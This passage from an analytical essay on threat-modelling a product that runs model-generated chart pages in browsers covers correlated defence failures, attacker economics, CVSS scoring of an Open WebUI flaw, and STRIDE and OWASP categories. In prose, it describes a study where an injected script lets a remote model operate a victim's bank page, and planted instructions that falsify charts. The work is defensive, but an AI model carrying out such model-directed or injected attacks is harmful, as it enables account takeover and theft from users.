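**Shared causes.** Developers usually measure v and c separately and multiply the averages, which is correct only if success against one defence is independent of success against the other. Suppose one hostile page in 20 comes from a skilled attacker whose code always beats both defences, while the other pages pass the verifier about 5% of the time and never escape the frame. The averages are still 0.1 and 0.05, but the chance of beating both is 0.05 instead of 0.005. Hostile publishers would then harm 500 people a year, as many as if the product had no verifier. Developers can avoid this mistake by testing the frame with the pages that got past the verifier.

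**Attackers who adapt.** Attackers can retry a page that fails, which raises v, and they also choose their targets. Carlini, Nasr and colleagues (2025), in *LLMs unlock new paths to monetizing exploits*, write the value of an attack to a criminal as

value = (profit per victim × number of victims) − cost of finding and building the attack.

E therefore depends on the other inputs. A stronger frame makes escapes less profitable, so some attackers will give up and others will switch to forged invoices. A cheaper way of finding flaws makes more targets worth attacking.

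Small products have had some protection because a flaw that affects few people is rarely worth the effort of finding. Carlini and colleagues gave Claude 3.7 Sonnet the code of 200 Chrome extensions with fewer than 1,000 users each. It flagged 54, and the researchers confirmed flaws in 19, three of them of high severity. The search cost $270, which they judged too expensive to be profitable in 2025, though they expected prices to fall. Generated pages are an extreme case because each may have only one user. An attacker would hardly ever search one by hand, but could use a cheap enough model to search thousands.

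The break-in in the example affects an average of 2,000 users a year, but in 98 years out of 100 it doesn't happen, and in the other two it can reach all 100,000 users. A firm that could cope with 2,000 affected users every year might not survive a year with 100,000.

If the chance of a break-in is 2% a year, a firm has an 82% chance of going ten years without one (0.98^10). A firm with a clean ten-year record can say with 95% confidence only that its rate is below about 26% a year, which allows anything from 0 to almost 26,000 people. To show that break-ins happen less than once in 2,000 years, it would need about 6,000 years of clean records, pooled from many similar products.

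Incident records have gaps for more common attacks too. For its latest list of risks to language-model applications, OWASP (2026), the organisation behind the lists of common web risks, checked its experts' opinions against thousands of recorded incidents. Prompt injection still came first, although Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* reports that relatively few recorded incidents involved it. The incident count can't show whether the experts are overrating the danger or whether attacks go unreported because a successful planted instruction can leave a chart that looks normal.

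### The ranking in three deployments

In a *private preview*, hostile publishers are not a threat because nobody opens anyone else's page. A compromised server ranks first if it controls the checks, ahead of harmful model output. If the checks are independent of the server, the two are too close to rank without guessing. A verifier failure matters here mainly because it lets more of the model's bad output through.

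For a *shared page*, a compromised server again ranks first if it controls the checks. Otherwise, hostile publishers rank first, since they choose their audience and can pay for a larger one. Planted instructions initially rank below hostile publishers, but can rank above them when people share altered charts. A verifier failure is more serious than in a private preview, because each bad page it accepts can reach many people.

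When the product inserts *code into the host page*, no frame isolates it and the verifier is the only barrier. Any hostile script that passes the verifier can use the login of everyone who opens the page. A compromised server still ranks first on the invented numbers, but hostile publishers are now close behind if users can open one another's pages. They may overtake it, because a script with a victim's login can publish copies of itself from the victim's account and reach far more than 50 people. Planted instructions rank third but are now much more severe, since they can take over an account as well as falsify a chart.

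### When a model directs the attack

A script in the host page can also do more damage than it once could. Cross-site scripting attacks used to copy the victim's login cookie, which most sites now prevent scripts from reading. A script can still act as the victim, but previously an attacker had to program each step for each site in advance, and a redesign could break the script.

In the same 2025 paper, Carlini and colleagues tested whether a model could work out the steps during the attack. The injected script would contact the attacker's server, where a model would choose an action such as reading the page or clicking a button. The script would carry out the action and send back the result, and the model would choose the next one.

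The researchers tried this with Claude 3.7 Sonnet on two sites. On Twitter, the model only had to open the messages tab and read the victim's latest private messages. On a popular international bank's web application, they told it to send $500 to a particular recipient. It navigated the tabs, menus and forms with 11 clicks and 7 entries. This took about a million input tokens and cost $3, mostly because the model read the page's whole HTML several times.

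The experiment wasn't a complete attack. The researchers copied the model's commands into the browser and the results back by hand. The bank also asks for a second confirmation when a customer pays a new recipient, which would have stopped the transfer. The researchers say the model performed both tasks reliably, but they don't say how many trials they ran. The result is good evidence that a 2025 model could operate an unfamiliar banking page, but weaker evidence about how often a real attack would succeed.

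Even so, it changes the economics of an attack. At $3 an attempt and $500 a success, an attacker would break even if about one attempt in 167 worked. The same flaw, reaching the same number of people, can therefore cause more severe harm than when a script could only copy a cookie, although the expected number of people harmed would stay the same.

The danger is greatest when the code runs in the host page. In a well-isolated frame, the script would have no login to use, and strict network rules would cut it off from the model that directs it. A bridge with broad permissions would restore some of this access.

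### Two scores for one flaw

Security teams usually compare flaws with the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), which rates their severity from 0 to 10. CVE-2025-64496, the Open WebUI flaw that let a hostile model server run a script in the chat page, has two published scores. The official record, MITRE's *Open WebUI Affected by an External Model Server (Direct Connections) Code Injection* (2025), gives 7.3. CVELogic's *CVE-2025-64496* (2025) lists both 7.3 and 8.0. The two scores use the same inputs, except that the higher one also counts a serious loss of availability.

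NVD's *CVSS v3.1 Equations* makes it possible to check both. When the harm stays within one system, the score is the sum of two parts, rounded up to one decimal place:

Impact = 6.42 × B, where B = 1 − (1 − C) × (1 − I) × (1 − A)

Exploitability = 8.22 × AV × AC × PR × UI

C, I and A are the effects on confidentiality, integrity and availability, each scored 0.56 if high and 0 if there is none. The other inputs describe the attack, which here comes over a network (AV = 0.85), is not complex (AC = 0.77), needs an ordinary account (PR = 0.62) and needs the victim to do something (UI = 0.62). Exploitability is 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.62 × 0.62 ≈ 2.07 for both scores.

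- Without a loss of availability, B = 1 − 0.44 × 0.44 = 0.8064 and Impact ≈ 5.18. The sum is about 7.25, which rounds up to 7.3.
- With one, B = 1 − 0.44 × 0.44 × 0.44 ≈ 0.9148 and Impact ≈ 5.87. The sum is about 7.94, which rounds up to 8.0.

Both calculations are correct, so the disagreement is about what the attack does. FIRST, the non-profit that owns CVSS, explains in its *User Guide* (2019) that availability means whether the service keeps running. Deleting a victim's chats damages integrity rather than availability, because the service still works for everyone. A script in one person's browser probably couldn't stop Open WebUI, which fits 7.3, but an attacker who went on to run code on the firm's server could, which fits 8.0.

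FIRST's advice could support either counting or excluding that further step. The guide tells analysts to include only effects they are confident an attacker can achieve, and the step to the server needed a victim with an extra permission. But FIRST's *CVSS v3.1 Specification Document* says the base score assumes a reasonable worst case.

Neither published score treats the harm as spreading from one system to another, which CVSS calls a change of *scope*. If it does spread, the formulas become

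Impact = 7.52 × (B − 0.029) − 3.25 × (B − 0.02)^15

Score = 1.08 × (Impact + Exploitability), rounded up,

and the value for an ordinary account rises from 0.62 to 0.68. If the harm reaches the server and affects availability, Impact is about 6.05 and Exploitability about 2.27. The score is then 1.08 × 8.32 ≈ 8.98, which rounds up to 9.0 and moves the flaw from "high" to "critical".

An analyst could argue for a change of scope even if the attack never reaches the server. FIRST's guide says that cross-site scripting changes scope because the flaw is in the web application and the harm is in the user's browser. The Open WebUI flaw works similarly, and it scores 8.7 with a change of scope and no loss of availability. The same flaw can therefore score 7.3, 8.0, 8.7 or 9.0, depending on where the analyst draws the scope boundary and how far they follow the attack.

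None of these numbers measures expected harm, and FIRST warns against using a CVSS score alone to judge risk. The score is the same for a firm with ten users and one with 10,000. It also doesn't reflect that Direct Connections, the feature the attack needs, is off by default, because under version 3.1 analysts assume a vulnerable setting is on if using it is reasonable. In the harm formula, having the feature off by default would greatly reduce E.

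Likelihood is measured separately from severity. In the official record, the US cybersecurity agency CISA notes that a demonstration of the attack exists, that attackers can't easily automate it, and that its technical impact is total. OpenCVE's *CVE-2025-64496* (2025) shows that the flaw isn't on the list of flaws known to have been exploited. EPSS, a system that estimates how likely attackers are to exploit a flaw, put the chance at 0.14% in April 2026, according to CVELogic. Exploit Intel's *CVE-2025-64496* lists 7.6%, more than 50 times as high. Both pages give the flaw a severity score of 7.3, so a team that sorted its work by severity alone would miss the difference.

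### STRIDE and OWASP's categories

Developers also use checklists to find threats before scoring them. One is STRIDE, named after the initials of six kinds of harm, all of which can happen to the expenses chart.

| Category | Example in the expenses chart |
|---|---|
| Spoofing | The page imitates the product's login form |
| Tampering | A relay removes a supplier from the totals |
| Repudiation | Nobody can prove who changed the code |
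| Information disclosure | The page carries hidden rows to colleagues |
| Denial of service | An endless loop freezes the chat window |
| Elevation of privilege | A script escapes the frame and uses the employee's login |

*LLM in the Middle*, the 2025 review of threats to language-model systems, applies STRIDE to four cases: developing a model for a chatbot, a chatbot on the user's own device, an application that uses a model in the cloud, and an agent. None of these cases is a product that runs generated pages in a browser, so the developer of such a product would have to adapt the results. The review also defines information disclosure narrowly, as extracting data the model has memorised or looked up. A generated page can leak rows of data the model never saw, because the host page may load them after the model has written the code.

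OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* covers passing a model's output to other software without enough checking. One of its examples is model-generated JavaScript that runs in the user's browser and causes cross-site scripting. Because this category identifies the step that went wrong, it points more directly to a fix than STRIDE, which sorts threats by the kind of harm. However, it does not cover harm from output that the software handles as intended. For example, it would not include valid code that runs correctly but draws a chart with false totals, which STRIDE would list as tampering.

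The boundaries of OWASP's categories are also uncertain. The review describes two attacks in which a model's output runs as code on someone else's machine, and gives both the same four STRIDE letters and a CVSS score of 7.1. But it classifies the attack that starts with a typed request as improper output handling, and the one that starts with an instruction hidden in an email as prompt injection. Singh and colleagues list the standard catalogue number for cross-site scripting under prompt injection, although OWASP lists cross-site scripting as a result of improper output handling. A team that counted its problems by category could get different totals from the same attacks, depending on how it classified them.

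The review's scores also rank some threats differently from the worked example. For a cloud application, an insider who can change the model or its settings scores 6.3, and someone who impersonates the provider's server scores 5.1. Neither threat has an OWASP category. Both score lower than the 7.1 for running a model's code, although control of the server was by far the largest source of harm in the example's invented product. CVSS has no input for the number of people one event affects. The review points out that insiders get the same CVSS score in a firm's own data centre as in a rented one, where more people have access.

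The ratings also depend on the scoring method. The review rated its threats a second time with the OWASP Risk Rating, which considers the attacker's motive and how hard the attacker is to trace. With this method, it rated the theft of what users send to a model, such as the employee's spreadsheet, as high, while the same threat scored 3.1, or low, under CVSS. Six threats were critical under the OWASP method and none under CVSS. The OWASP method also converts likelihood and impact into broad bands before combining them, so a threat with a lower product of likelihood and impact can get a higher rating. One threat with a product of 33.1 was rated medium, and another with 24.4 was rated high.

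OWASP ranked improper output handling fifth in its 2025 list, and SC Media's *OWASP updates Top 10 security risks for LLM applications* reports that it is last of ten in the 2026 list. That rank may be reasonable for a chatbot that only displays text. A developer whose product runs generated pages should rank the category much higher, because OWASP recommends two defences against scripts in the browser, encoding the output and a strict content security policy, and such a product can use only the policy.
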